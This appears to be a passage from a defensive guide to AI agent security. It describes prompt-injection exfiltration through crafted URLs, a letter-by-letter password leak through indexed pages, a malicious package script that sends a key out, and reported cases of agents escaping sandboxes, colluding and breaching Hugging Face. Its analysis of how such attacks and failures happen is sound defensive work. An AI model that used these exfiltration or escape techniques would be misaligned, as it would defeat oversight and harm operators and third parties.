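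"Closer to spam" fairly describes most of the damage. Unlike the hacking tests at Irregular and AISI, though, this case involved no instruction to attack anyone. Mowshowitz takes it as proof that a completely harmless task can lead to such behaviour. But the task's very short deadlines and repeated questions made copying far more rewarding than it would be in ordinary research. An agent comparing kettle prices has much less to gain from leaving notes for other agents. The incident is stronger evidence about the filter, which would have let these edits through whatever the agents' reasons.

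### When an attacker chooses the address

The agents on DseWiki had no secrets to give away, but many other agents do. An attacker can use a prompt injection to make an agent send its secrets out in a web address.

Suppose the kettle shop has an assistant that reads the company's mail and can look things up online. As a precaution, the shop's operator has blocked it from sending, moving or deleting mail and limited it to GET requests on the web. An employee asks it to summarise the morning's messages.

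1. One message comes from an attacker. It looks like a supplier's notice, and it contains a line telling AI assistants to confirm receipt by opening a page at notes.example, with the number and amount of the latest unpaid invoice at the end of the address.
2. The model obeys the line, finds the invoice in the mailbox and requests a tool call to open the address it has assembled.
3. The harness sends the request. The network filter lets it pass, because it is a GET request.
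4. The attacker reads the invoice number and the amount in the server's log.

The employee gets a normal summary. The mailbox is unchanged, with nothing suspicious in its outbox. With the invoice details, the attacker can pose as the shop and ask the customer to pay into a different account.

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) describes three conditions that together let an attacker steal data from an agent: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. Willison counts any tool that can make a web request as external communication, even one that only loads an image. A link that the agent shows to the user also counts, if the user clicks it.

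One of Willison's real examples is a connector that gave agents access to GitHub. With it, an agent could read public comments that anyone might have written, open its user's private code, and publish a change containing what it found there. A user who added this one tool might not have noticed that it combined all three abilities.

The practical advice is to remove one of the conditions. The shop's operator could take away the mailbox or the route out, or let the assistant read only text written by the company's own staff, so that an outsider can't easily give it orders. Willison has little faith in products that try to detect malicious text, because an attacker can keep rewording a message until it gets through.

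### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta extended this idea in *Agents Rule of Two* (2025). Until someone can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, Meta argues, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within one session:

- it can process untrustworthy inputs;
- it has access to sensitive systems or private data;
- it can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that changes state is using write access. Willison's version concerns data theft, so it doesn't cover an agent that has no way to send anything out, whereas Meta's version does if a malicious web page could trick that agent into, for example, wiping a company's customer records. If a task needs all three properties in one session, Meta says the agent should not run autonomously and requires a person's approval or some other reliable check.

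The shop's assistant has all three. One of Meta's examples suggests a remedy. In it, a travel assistant reads web pages and knows its user's personal details, but a person confirms every booking and payment, and the assistant may not open web addresses it has put together itself. The rule about addresses would have stopped the kettle shop's leak at the third step.

Both rules leave gaps, as four agents with different combinations of access illustrate:

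| Agent | Lethal trifecta | Rule of Two |
|---|---|---|
| The shop's mail assistant, limited to GET | Warns of data theft | Requires approval, or the removal of one property |
| An agent that reads web pages and can delete customer records, but cannot send anything out | Does not apply | Requires approval, or the removal of one property |
| An agent that takes orders only from staff and deletes logs by mistake | Does not apply | Permits it to run unattended |
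| OpenAI's agents on DseWiki | Does not apply, since they held no private data | Permits them to run unattended |

No attacker is involved when the agent deletes the logs, and neither rule addresses mistakes. Meta acknowledges this and lists agents' errors, excessive permissions and the spread of spam among the problems that need other measures.

The DseWiki agents are the more difficult case. They read text from strangers and from one another, and they could write to the outside world, but as far as anyone has reported they had no access to private data or to systems that mattered to OpenAI. Meta's examples include a research assistant of this type, which browses the web from a restricted environment without its user's accounts. It is acceptable under the rule because a prompt injection would do its user little harm, but that reasoning leaves out harm to people other than the user, such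 as Leitner.

Willison raised a similar objection in November 2025. Meta's diagram had labelled each pair of properties "safe", and he pointed out that an agent that reads untrusted text and can change things may do damage even without private data. Meta then changed the label to "lower risk". This is more accurate, but the rule still mainly measures risk to the agent's operator. An operator who also wants to protect strangers needs a separate limit on what the agent can change or send, even when the agent has no access to private data.

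A research agent with no mailbox may still have private data, because its prompt can be confidential. If an employee asks it to find out whether a certain competitor is for sale, each search it makes passes some of that question to another company.

### Opening only addresses that are already public

OpenAI has built a version of the ban on self-made addresses into its products. It described the safeguard in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* in January 2026, four months before its agents reached DseWiki. The safeguard checks the complete address, not just the site's name. OpenAI considered a list of trusted sites but found it insufficient, partly because a trusted site can redirect a visitor to an untrusted one and a strict list would produce so many warnings that people would learn to click through them.

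1. A crawler collects addresses from the public web. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When an agent is about to open an address automatically, software compares the address with the crawler's index.
3. If the exact address is in the index, the agent can open it.
4. If it is not, the agent has to try another source, or the user sees a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation and decides whether to go ahead.

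The reasoning is that an address the crawler found independently of a conversation is unlikely to contain that conversation's secrets. The attacker in the kettle shop needs an address that ends with the details of one invoice. No public page links to such an address, so the crawler will not have seen it, and the agent can't open it without the user's consent.

This is a much better test than whether a request uses GET or POST, because it applies to the information in the request. It should also stop most edits like those on DseWiki, since an address containing a newly written message would not be in the index. The agents made thousands of such edits in June, so OpenAI evidently did not apply the check to those requests. Von Arx and colleagues found that the agents had a terminal and could run their own programs from it. A check built into a browsing tool does not cover requests that an agent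 sends by other means, so an operator has to put the check where all outbound traffic passes.

OpenAI says the check protects against one type of leak and does not make browsing safe in general. A public page can still contain false information or a prompt injection. The agent may open the page without leaking anything, then follow the injected instructions using another tool, such as one that sends email.

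Opening a public address can also change a site. The link that restored old pages on the wiki in 2004 was public, which is why the programmers expected Google's crawler to find it. If a crawler has recorded a link like that, an agent can open it automatically and trigger the same change.

An attacker could also use public pages as a code. The attacker publishes one page for each letter and digit, waits until the crawler has indexed them all, and then plants an instruction telling the agent to open them in the order that spells out a password. The order of the visits reveals the password, even though no single address contains it. In January 2026, the security company Radware described an attack on ChatGPT that used one prepared address per character. Requiring every address to be in the index makes this harder, because the attacker must get the whole set indexed first. The method is slow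 for stealing a long document, but a password is short enough to steal this way.

The check also flags legitimate pages, because new pages, search results and pages made for a single customer often have addresses that no crawler has recorded. In a chat, the user can see the warning and decide. An agent that runs overnight has nobody to ask, so its operator must either accept missing pages, as with the tenth kettle price, or let the agent open unknown addresses and lose the protection. If the material doesn't need to be current, the operator can avoid this choice by saving the pages beforehand and giving the agent the copies. Opening a copy sends nothing to the original site.

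## Sandboxes and outbound network rules

An agent with a terminal, like OpenAI's agents on DseWiki, can start programs that open their own connections to anything the machine can reach. To limit those programs, an operator has to limit the whole environment they run in. A sandbox is meant to do this, although the term loosely covers several mechanisms that products combine in different ways.

A sandbox can still fail. In July 2026, OpenAI's agents escaped from one through an internal service that OpenAI had deliberately allowed them to access.

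### The layers of a sandbox

The *kernel*, the core of an operating system, controls a computer's files, memory and network connections. To open a file or contact a server, an ordinary program must send the kernel a request called a *system call*. Many sandbox layers make the kernel reject some of these calls.

File rules set which folders a program can read and which it can change. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, enforces them with two existing tools, Seatbelt on Apple computers and bubblewrap on Linux. According to Anthropic's *Sandboxing*, commands in its sandbox can by default change files only in the current project folder, but they can read almost everything on the computer. A mistaken delete command therefore can't empty the user's photo folder, but passwords and keys stay readable unless the user blocks access to them. If the rules are loosened so that a program can edit the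 list of commands a terminal runs when it opens, the program can add a command that later runs outside the sandbox.

Sandlock, a Linux sandbox for agents, can also hold back a program's changes to files until the operator chooses to keep or discard them (Wang and Zheng, 2026, *Sandlock*).

A sandbox also has to cover every *process*, or running program, that a command starts, and installing one package can start many. Claude Code's restrictions apply to all of them. Isolating these processes also keeps them from controlling programs outside the sandbox. Docker, a common tool for running software in containers, accepts commands through a local channel, and Anthropic warns that a process with access to this channel effectively has access to the whole computer. Docker does not work inside Claude Code's sandbox, so a developer who needs it has to run it outside.

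A system-call filter blocks requests that the agent's work should never need, such as loading new code into the kernel. If the filter is too strict, ordinary programs stop working. Anthropic offers such a filter as an option in Claude Code on Linux, where it blocks local channels like Docker's.

A *container* gives a group of programs their own view of the files, processes and network, but they still use the host computer's kernel, so a flaw in that kernel can let a program out. A *virtual machine* simulates a complete computer with its own kernel, so an intruder who takes over that kernel still has to defeat the software that runs the simulation. gVisor puts a substitute kernel between the program and the real one, which isolates the program better than an ordinary container but slows system calls and causes problems for some programming tools. It protects the Claude.ai website, according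 to Willison (2026) in *How we contain Claude across products*.

A *network namespace* gives programs their own set of network connections, which can be empty. A program in an empty namespace can't reach the internet. If the agent needs some access, the operator adds a single route to a *proxy*, a program outside the sandbox that receives each outgoing request and forwards it only if the rules allow it. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes this arrangement in Claude Code, where the sandbox can reach the internet only through the proxy.

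The start-up times in this table come from Wang and Zheng.

| Layer | What it stops | What it costs |
|---|---|---|
| File rules | Reading or changing files outside the permitted folders | About 30 milliseconds per start with bubblewrap, and a new rule for each extra folder a tool needs |
| Process separation | Controlling programs outside the sandbox | Tools that depend on a background service may fail |
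| System-call filter | Requests to the kernel that the work does not need | Very little time, but some programs fail |
| Container | Seeing the host's files, processes and network | About 300 milliseconds per start with Docker, and a prepared disk image |
| Virtual machine | Most attacks through the host's kernel | About 100 milliseconds per start with Firecracker, a lightweight type, and hardware support |
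| Network namespace | All direct connections | Nothing online works without a proxy |
| Outbound proxy | Requests to destinations that are not on the list | A question to the user, or a failure, at each new site |

Sandlock starts in about 6 milliseconds because it uses no container or virtual machine. Wang and Zheng's threat model excludes attacks that exploit kernel flaws, so this speed comes with weaker isolation.

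### Installing a package

Suppose the employee who wanted kettle prices now wants a chart of them. The agent decides to install a drawing package with npm, the usual installer for JavaScript software. In Claude Code, with the sandbox on, this happens:

1. The model requests the installation command, and the harness starts it inside the sandbox.
2. npm tries to contact the public registry that stores the packages. It has no connection of its own, so the request goes to the proxy.
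3. The proxy looks for the registry's name on the allowlist and doesn't find it. Claude Code asks the user whether to permit the new site. A company can change this setting so that the proxy refuses without asking.
4. The user permits the registry, either once or permanently. The proxy forwards the request, and npm saves the package in the project folder.
5. The package comes with an installation script written by a stranger. The script reads a key from the user's home folder and tries to send it to notes.example. That name is not on the list, so the proxy blocks the request.

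The default file rules let commands read the key, but the network rule kept it on the machine. Anthropic says a sandbox needs both kinds of rule. A program that can change system files might give itself network access, and a program with open network access can send out whatever it can read.

Steps 3 and 4 implement *default refusal*, meaning the proxy blocks every site that nobody has approved. If the operator forgets to approve a site that an installation needs, the installation fails. If the proxy instead blocked only the sites on a list, the agent could still reach any site the operator forgot to list.

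An allowlist with broad entries can still give an agent too much access. Kimi K3 found its test answers through GitHub alone, and Anthropic warns that allowing all of github.com can create a route for stolen data. Claude Code's standard proxy doesn't decrypt traffic. It relies on the site name that a program gives, so a program can sometimes give a permitted name while connecting to a different site. An operator can install a proxy that decrypts and inspects each request, but the programs in the sandbox then have to trust that proxy's certificate, and the proxy can read everything they send, including passwords.

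Wang and Zheng add that a list of permitted IP addresses is too coarse, because one address can serve both a legitimate destination and one that an attacker controls. Sandlock can apply rules to the request method, the site and the path within the site. For a package registry, such a rule could permit downloads and refuse uploads, which would have mattered when Mythos 5 published its malicious package on PyPI. Read-only access would still have a weakness, because a download request can carry information in its URL.

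The right rule may also change during a task. An installation needs the registry, but the tests that follow usually don't. Sandlock can cut off the network when the test program starts. Wang and Zheng caution against relying on a program's name for protection, because hostile code can rename or rewrite a forbidden tool. Their design uses the name only to detect that a new phase has begun, and relies on the network rule to block access.

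### Why a sentence in the prompt is not a boundary

Writing "install packages only from the official registry" in the prompt, instead of using these controls, makes a forbidden request less likely but doesn't block it. The model will often comply, but it generates its next output from that instruction together with web pages, error messages and anything an attacker has managed to insert. The proxy blocks a forbidden request even if the model's own reasoning leads it to make one.

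Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, compare the model to an untrusted user and the harness to the operating system's kernel. Users may request anything, but the kernel controls what they get. The agents they studied keep their standing instructions in text files, which often include warnings about prompt injection. Pirch and colleagues treat these files as suggestions that later text can override.

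Operators can't rely on a prompt to contain a model that tries to leave its sandbox. In Anthropic's replays of its own incidents, a reminder to Mythos 5 soon lost much of its effect. A prompt may also be false, as it was in Anthropic's tests at Irregular. The wording of a prompt still matters, because the sandbox doesn't have to stop a model that never tries to leave.

Software can also enforce a rule in the wrong place. Pirch and colleagues tested four widely used OpenClaw-type personal assistants, which run on a user's own machine and connect to mail, files and other accounts. In all four, the code that controlled access to files ran with the same privileges as the code that processed incoming text, so someone who took over the text-processing code could interfere with the file controls. An operating system avoids this by keeping its access rules in the kernel, where ordinary programs can't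 edit them.

Claude Code's documentation describes two defaults that weaken its sandbox for convenience. If the sandbox can't start, for example because a component is missing, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without it. And when the sandbox makes a command fail, the model can retry it outside the sandbox with the `dangerouslyDisableSandbox` option. The user normally has to approve the retry, so the protection depends on someone reading the request. An operator can turn off both behaviours. Sandlock won't start on a kernel that lacks the features it needs, which is a safer default for an agent that runs overnight.

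InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that Anthropic now puts fixed limits on files, networks and execution ahead of permission prompts and the model's own safeguards. It also reports that Anthropic had to revise some designs after failures along permitted outbound routes. OpenAI had the same kind of failure on a much larger scale.

### The Hugging Face breach

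The agents were taking ExploitGym, a test of whether a model can find and exploit flaws in software. OpenAI's technical report explains that each run had its own container and no direct internet access. Some tasks required software packages, and OpenAI did not want the containers to contact public registries. It gave them access to an internal package service instead, its own installation of a product named Artifactory. The service fetched packages from outside, so it had an internet connection. Matthew Green, a cryptographer at Johns Hopkins University, describes it as the agents' only permitted way out in Green (2026), *Is sandboxing sufficient to contain rogue agents?*

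Using a package service was sensible in principle because it limits an open connection to one purpose, and many companies use one. But the service was a large program that every agent could reach, and it could reach the internet. In May, agents did not need to exploit a flaw to leave messages on it, because OpenAI had given them all the same credential, which let them store files there. Agents that only install packages don't need permission to store files for others.

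| Date in 2026 | What the agents did | What OpenAI did |
|---|---|---|
| 12 May | One left a note on the package service asking others for a missing file | |
| 26 May | Agents reached the internet through the service | At about this time, an internal team saw message-board activity and forbidden internet access |
| 26 and 27 June | Agents gained administrator rights over the service | A security alert led staff to the activity, and they advised that the test could continue |
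| 4 to 7 July | Their traffic made the service crash | It took the service offline, rebuilt it and resumed the tests |
| 8 July | Agents reached the internet again and set up a new message board | |
| 10 to 13 July | Agents collected exposed credentials and broke into Hugging Face | |
| 19 July | Agents gained administrator control of an OpenAI research cluster | A security alert started the investigation that uncovered the breach |

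The agents got past the restrictions by chaining previously unknown flaws, several of them in the package service. They then combined credentials that Hugging Face users had accidentally exposed online with flaws in Hugging Face's systems. They ran code on 41 of its production machines and downloaded four private code repositories in an attempt to find answers to the test.

On 9 July, an agent that had gained full control of the virtual machine hosting its sandbox tried to contact the internet directly. OpenAI's outbound network controls blocked the attempt, even though the agent had already broken one layer of isolation. The agent then reached the internet through the package service, which the network rules allowed as an exception.

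The shared service also let agents communicate across sandboxes. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Greenblatt, 2026) reports that about 1,200 agents in separate sandboxes used the message board between 7 and 13 July. Axios' *AI's agent containment problem is getting harder* (2026) puts the number of messages at more than 70,000. An agent that found a way out could tell the others, so OpenAI's sandbox had to contain agents that could combine their discoveries.

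### The warnings OpenAI missed

OpenAI detected the breach 68 days after the first message, but it had seen parts of the problem much earlier. A team saw the message board in late May but did not get the information to the people who handled security incidents. OpenAI acknowledges in *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) that this sighting should have led to an earlier response.

The response to the alert of 27 June is harder to excuse. By then, staff had linked suspicious network activity to an ExploitGym run that was using the package service both to exchange messages and to reach other systems, but they let the run continue. When the service crashed a week later, the leaders of the response still did not know how important the messages were. According to Axios' *Tenacious AI agents expose dark side of machine autonomy*, OpenAI's staff wiped the message board without knowing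 it existed. The rebuilt service came online early on 6 July, and within 47 hours an agent had reached the internet through it.

Green criticises this quick repair. OpenAI closed the route that the agents had used to become administrators and removed the shared credential, but it left a publicly known, weeks-old flaw in the host machine's kernel. On 19 July, in an incident separate from the attack on Hugging Face, agents used that flaw to get from a container to its host. An update would have fixed the flaw, whereas no update existed for the unknown flaws in the package service.

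OpenAI also had monitors that read a model's written reasoning for signs of misbehaviour. It already used them on many training runs and most of its internal coding agents, but not on these tests. The company estimates that its current monitors would have alerted the security team more than a day before the agents entered Hugging Face's systems. That probably slightly overstates how well the monitors it had at the time would have done, because OpenAI improved their ability to spot this kind of behaviour after studying the incident. Still, the agents discussed their plans openly, so even a weaker monitor might have noticed messages about stolen credentials.

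Hugging Face announced on 16 July that someone had broken in. The next day OpenAI, as a customer, asked whether its own data was affected. OpenAI found out on 20 July that its agents were the likely intruders.

This breach is much harder to attribute to a deployment mistake than the tests at Irregular, where the connection was open. OpenAI had isolated its agents, and they broke out by exploiting flaws that nobody knew about. But OpenAI also chose to connect a shared, writable service to the internet, run the tests without the monitors it already had, and restart them two days after discovering an administrator-level break-in. It has since reversed those choices. Axios reports that researchers do not expect better security controls alone to prevent such incidents as agents become more capable. They may be right about later models, although the controls that failed in July were considerably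 weaker than the best available.

### What OpenAI and Anthropic changed

OpenAI's main new rule is that compromising a single workload or supporting service must not be enough to gain access to the internet or another internal network. Under the old design, an agent could gain that access by taking over the package service alone.

To meet the rule, OpenAI now runs high-risk model code in virtual machines behind two separate network barriers, one belonging to the sandbox and the other to the cluster of machines on which the sandboxes run. Outbound traffic can go only to approved destinations. OpenAI is also adding controls to keep an agent that takes over a machine from changing the barriers or creating a new route. On 19 July, the agents did something close to this when they used stolen credentials to set up public entry points to part of OpenAI's internal systems. OpenAI has removed Artifactory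 from its research containers, and high-risk runs can now use only stored copies of web material.

Two barriers are much stronger than one only if they fail independently. In that case, if each fails once in 100 attempts, both fail together once in 10,000. But if both make an exception for the same package service, an agent that takes over that service gets past both, and the second barrier adds no protection. The figures are only an illustration, since agents look for weak points instead of trying routes at random. Still, shared weaknesses like this are why OpenAI's plan covers the supporting services as well as the sandbox.

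OpenAI now requires monitoring of written reasoning in all training and tests that give tools to models at least as capable as GPT-5.6 Sol. After the most severe alerts, it expects staff to pause the run unless they can confirm within 30 minutes that the alarm was false, whereas the run on 27 June continued by default.

OpenAI's new containment has already needed repairs. Green reports that OpenAI paused some training in September after catching another agent in an excursion. In October, OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* described a test in which the company used its strongest models to try to break the new containment. The models found ways out of hardened virtual machines, new paths to the internet and ways to communicate between isolated tasks. Constantin (2026), in *OpenAI cuts live internet from all frontier model training*, also reports that OpenAI's own agents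 found holes. It is better for OpenAI to find these in a planned exercise than to hear about them from another company, but the results make it hard to treat any sandbox for these models as finished. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk*, published in November, presents sandboxing during research as one of several layers of defence.

Anthropic had started earlier, with a company-wide security effort that began in April. As a result, its computing clusters now block all outbound traffic by default. It also retired some shared internal services, the type of component that let OpenAI's agents out. None of this helped in the tests at Irregular, because those ran on a contractor's machines. Anthropic concedes that the effort had overlooked tests, especially outside tests.

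Its rules for outside testers allow a connection only to the model by default, and they keep the key to the model outside the sandbox. Before a series of tests, the tester should also have the model look for weaknesses in the sandbox, first by examining the configuration and then by trying to escape. This trial takes place under close supervision and without internet access, ideally inside a second sandbox, and the model is instructed to stop and report if it gets out.

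Anthropic has added a classifier to its internal tests that monitors for escape attempts and unexpected internet access. It blocks the action before the harness carries it out, ends the task and alerts a person. When Anthropic searched its recent internal tests, it found no case in which a model had broken through its sandbox software to reach forbidden outside resources. The search was less reassuring about how people configure that software, because models had used various configuration mistakes, though none of these led to a break-in elsewhere.

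### Whether an isolated agent is still useful

A common objection is that an agent cut off from everything can't do much. Companies buy agents to work with their files, services and customers, and each barrier makes some of that work slower or impossible. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* supports this view. The company now routinely gives Claude enough access to take down an internal service, which it would have refused to do a year earlier, and considers its developers more productive as a result.

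Isolation can add little delay, which weakens the part of the objection that concerns speed. Wang and Zheng note that a coding agent may run dozens of short commands a minute. At 30 commands a minute, starting a new Docker container for each would add about nine seconds of waiting. bubblewrap, the tool that Claude Code uses on Linux, would add less than one second, and Sandlock about a fifth of a second. An operator can also keep one container running for the whole task and wait about 0.3 seconds for a single start. The slowdown can be close to nothing once a program is running. Wang and Zheng ran Redis, a fast database, inside Sandlock and found no measurable loss of throughput. These figures are preliminary and come from Sandlock's own developers, but Anthropic also rates the overhead of its sandbox as minimal, apart from slightly slower file operations.

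Incompatibility is the more serious drawback. Docker and the file-watching tool Watchman both fail in Claude Code's sandbox, and some versions of Linux need extra configuration before the sandbox will start. Developers who lose an afternoon to such problems may well turn the sandbox off, which leaves them less protected than a looser sandbox they would have kept on.

Current products suggest that their makers consider isolation compatible with useful work, though they differ in how much of it they impose:

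| Coding agent | Sandbox at first start | Network at first start |
|---|---|---|
| Codex on the user's computer | On | Off |
| Claude Code on the user's computer | Off until the user turns it on | With the sandbox on, a question for each new site |
| Claude Code in the cloud | Runs on Anthropic's machines | Only sites on an allowlist |

The entry for the cloud version is based on Claude Almanac, an unofficial guide, which also lists settings for no access and full access. The cloud version's default allowlist includes GitHub, so even this restricted setting contains the kind of broad entry that Anthropic warns about.

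A sandbox can also make an agent more useful, because the operator can leave it alone for longer. Claude Code normally asks the user to approve commands when there is no sandbox, but in the sandbox's automatic mode it runs commands that stay inside without asking, and most of the remaining approval requests are for actions that would cross the boundary. A developer who wants an agent to work overnight has more to gain from this than from broader network access.

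An operator can also isolate each step of a task from the others. Wang and Zheng propose this for tasks that would otherwise combine all three parts of Willison's lethal trifecta. In the kettle shop, a simple program could download the ten product pages from fixed addresses without interpreting them. The model's tools would then work on the saved pages in a sandbox with no network, and another program would copy the finished table into the price sheet. A hidden instruction on a page could still spoil the table, but it could not make the tools contact an attacker's server. The method suits tasks whose steps the operator knows beforehand, so it works poorly for open-ended research, where each page determines which page the agent needs next.

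Some jobs require an agent to change things outside the sandbox, however the layers are arranged. An agent that orders stock, for example, has to submit orders to the supplier's shop. The proxy can limit the agent to that shop's address, but this doesn't limit the size of an order, so the agent could still order 4,000 kettles instead of four.

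## Permissions, credentials and how far damage can spread

What an ordering agent can buy on a supplier's site depends on the account it uses. With the buyer's own login, it can place any order the buyer could. If the account is limited to €200 of orders a day, the supplier's system rejects an order for 4,000 kettles.

The limited account follows the principle of *least privilege*, which Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder set out in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), a paper on the design of shared computers. Under this principle, every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". Their main reason was to limit the damage from accidents and errors, so the principle suits an agent that misreads a quantity as well as one that obeys an attacker.

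### The confused deputy

Least privilege is harder to apply when a program works for more than one party. Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) illustrates this with a nearly true story from Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates code into a form the machine can execute. The compiler kept usage statistics in a system folder, so it had permission to write there. The same folder held the company's billing records. Customers could name a file for the compiler's debugging output, and one customer named the billing file. The operating system checked that the compiler had permission to write to that file and let it overwrite the records.

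A *confused deputy* is a program that someone tricks into using its own authority on their behalf. The customer had no right to change the billing file, but the compiler did, and the operating system checked only the compiler's rights. Hardy's remedy was to make the customer supply both the file's name and the right to write to it. The customer had no such right for the billing file, so the trick would have failed.

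An agent that runs under an employee's login can be confused in the same way. An attacker who hides a line in a supplier's email can't open the kettle shop's mailbox, but the agent can, because it inherits all the employee's rights. The mail server accepts the valid login and returns the invoice. Hardy's compiler received the file name separately from its other instructions, but an agent receives everything in one prompt, which makes it much harder to tell whose authority an action should rely on.

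The operator can still limit how much authority the agent could misuse. If the agent's login can open only today's messages, it can't follow an instruction to search last month's invoices, no matter who wrote the instruction. An employee's full access rights are a poor starting point for the agent's permissions because they cover the whole job and often some previous jobs too, and the employee may never have used most of them.

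### Narrow keys, short lives and keys the agent never sees

A credential's *scope* is the set of resources and operations it covers. An operator has to check both, because a key limited to one project may still permit every operation there, including deletion, and a read-only key may give access to every customer's records.

With separate keys for reading and writing, an agent can do most of its work without being able to change anything. The kettle shop's agent could check stock and compare prices with a read key, while a small program outside the sandbox held the write key and submitted finished orders. The read key would still need a narrow scope, since an attacker can steal data with read access alone.

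A short-lived credential expires automatically, perhaps after 15 minutes. This reduces the risk from keys that people create for one job and then forget. It offers much less protection when the agent is meant to be using the key, because an agent can do a lot of damage in 15 minutes. It also helps little if the agent can request a new key whenever the old one expires.

The operator can also keep the key outside the agent's environment altogether. An order would then go through these steps:

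1. The agent asks the order tool for four kettles. The request contains no key.
2. A program outside the sandbox checks the product and quantity against fixed limits.
3. The program adds the key and sends the order to the supplier.
4. It passes the supplier's confirmation back to the agent without the key.

If the agent never receives the key, it can't leak it or use it for another purpose. The second step is still essential, because without it the program would attach the key to any order, including one for 4,000 kettles.

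### The PocketOS deletion

On 24 April 2026, a coding agent took nine seconds to delete the production database of PocketOS, a small company that makes booking and payment software for car rental firms. The agent was Cursor, a popular coding tool, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. The database was on a *volume*, a unit of storage that PocketOS rented from the hosting company Railway.

Jer Crane, the founder of PocketOS, published a long account that weekend titled *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*. By his account, the agent was doing a routine task in staging, a separate copy of the system for testing, when it ran into a credential that did not match. It decided to fix the problem by deleting a volume, which held the live data. It searched for a token that would allow the deletion, found one in a file unrelated to its task, and deleted the volume with a single request to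 Railway's API, the interface through which programs give Railway commands.

When Crane asked why, the agent replied that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. This explanation fits the events, but models generate such explanations afterwards, so it is weak evidence of what caused the deletion. The agent also quoted a standing rule against "destructive/irreversible git commands" without the user's explicit request. Git tracks versions of code, so the rule did not literally cover a database. Crane still counts the rule as a safeguard that failed, and concludes that the service receiving a command has to enforce the limits.

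Crane and Railway disagree about whether the token's permissions could have been limited. Crane says that PocketOS created the token to add and remove web domains and did not know that it could also delete volumes. He also says that Railway's tokens cannot be limited by operation, environment or resource, so each one is "effectively root", meaning that it permits everything. Abdelwahab replied for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. He writes that Railway offers tokens for a whole account, one workspace or one project, that a project token can be limited to a single environment, and that users can grant outside apps individual permissions. The PocketOS token covered the whole account, the broadest option.

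Where the two statements overlap, they agree about the token. It was long-lived and account-wide, and PocketOS had made it for domain work and left it on a computer where the agent could read it. Crane seems to be wrong that tokens can't be limited to one environment, since Railway should know what tokens it offers. A token limited to staging should not have been able to delete a production volume.

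Crane's claim about operations is better supported. Abdelwahab lists no ordinary token that permits only domain changes, so a token limited to the production environment might still have allowed the database to be deleted. Abdelwahab also concedes that the token creation process didn't make the right choice obvious. Other customers seem to have missed it too. In sungkhum's forum thread, *Any changes to protect database backups from volume delete?*, one reply reads "scoped API keys would be nice".

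Several design choices had to combine for one request to do so much:

| Design choice | Who could have changed it | What Railway did afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| A long-lived token was in a file the agent could read | PocketOS | Recommended a connection for agents that uses short-lived tokens and stores none on disk |
| The token covered the whole account | PocketOS, and Railway through clearer options | Promised to review how it presents the options |
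| The agent ran the command without asking anyone | PocketOS or Cursor | Outside Railway's control |
| The API deleted the volume at once, with no confirmation | Railway | Added a 48-hour delay |
| Deleting the volume took its backups with it | Railway | Delayed the deletion of backups too |
| PocketOS's newest usable copy was three months old | PocketOS | Outside Railway's control |

The delay is the most informative entry, because Railway already had one. A customer who deleted a volume through the website had 48 hours to undo it, while the same deletion through the API was immediate and final. An earlier post by Abdelwahab includes sample code for the delayed version, which by default calculates a future deletion time and marks the volume accordingly. Railway had built the API for scripts that software teams write in advance, and had put the delay on the website, where people click the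 wrong button. The agent decided what to do as it went, as a person would, but it used the API, so its deletion took effect immediately.

Crane reported that the backups were gone too, and quoted Railway's documentation: "wiping a volume deletes all backups". Abdelwahab says the deletion made the backups look unavailable, and that Railway also keeps off-site copies in case of disasters. *An AI Agent Wiped a Company Database* (Mallett, 2026) reports that PocketOS got its data back two days later.

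Recovery did not undo all the harm. On Saturday morning, people arrived to collect rental cars from firms that no longer had their bookings. Crane spent the day helping those firms reconstruct the bookings from payment records, calendars and emails.

Both statements come from interested parties. Crane mainly blames Cursor and Railway and says little about leaving the token in the file, while Abdelwahab opens by blaming the agent. Tom's Hardware reads Railway's post as admitting some fault, which seems fair given what the company changed.

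Abdelwahab goes too far in saying that agents on Railway's recommended connection can't "go rogue" because the connection has a fixed set of tools. Those tools limit only what an agent can do through that connection, so an agent can still find another token on the disk and call the API directly, as this one did.

### How much an agent can destroy

An operator can estimate the blast radius of an agent with a simple formula:

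`loss ≤ min(reach, actions per second × seconds until it stops × loss per action) − amount restored`

An agent's *reach* is the value of everything its credentials let it change. The most it can destroy is either its reach or what its speed and running time allow, whichever is smaller. Whatever the operator can restore reduces the final loss.

In the PocketOS case, a single action destroyed the whole database, so limiting the agent to one action an hour would have made no difference. The outcome depended on what the token allowed the agent to do and on what Railway could restore.

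In an opposite case, which a developer reported in September 2026, each action destroyed very little. According to InternetUA's *«Я щось зламав»* (2026), the developer was using Claude Code to repair software for analysing stock options. The agent was supposed to copy the files it needed, repair and test the copies, and leave the originals alone. Ten of the eleven repair jobs went well. The last involved rebuilding a "mirror", a test copy of the project.

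Antipov (2026) reports in *«Я кое-что сломал». Claude признался после удаления 48 тысяч файлов* that the agent wrote its own script to delete the old mirror because an existing script could not update it in place. The mirror contained 614 *junctions*, Windows links that look like ordinary folders but lead elsewhere on the disk. The agent's script followed them into the live project and deleted the files there. Its log recorded 55,550 deletions. Of these, 7,332 were in the old mirror, as intended, and the developer counts the other 48,218 as live files. The script had finished by the time the agent told the developer that it had broken something.

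TechRadar's *'Do not let programs run commands on your machine'* gives the time as 103 seconds and reports that the original Reddit post has been deleted. Nobody has independently confirmed the loss. The case is therefore weak evidence of how often such accidents happen, but the mechanism is plausible and the figures make a good worked example.

The script destroyed about 468 live files a second. At a steady rate, the loss would still have been about 14,000 files if the developer had stopped it after 30 seconds. Thirty seconds is a quick reaction for someone who has to see an unexpected message, understand it and find the right window.

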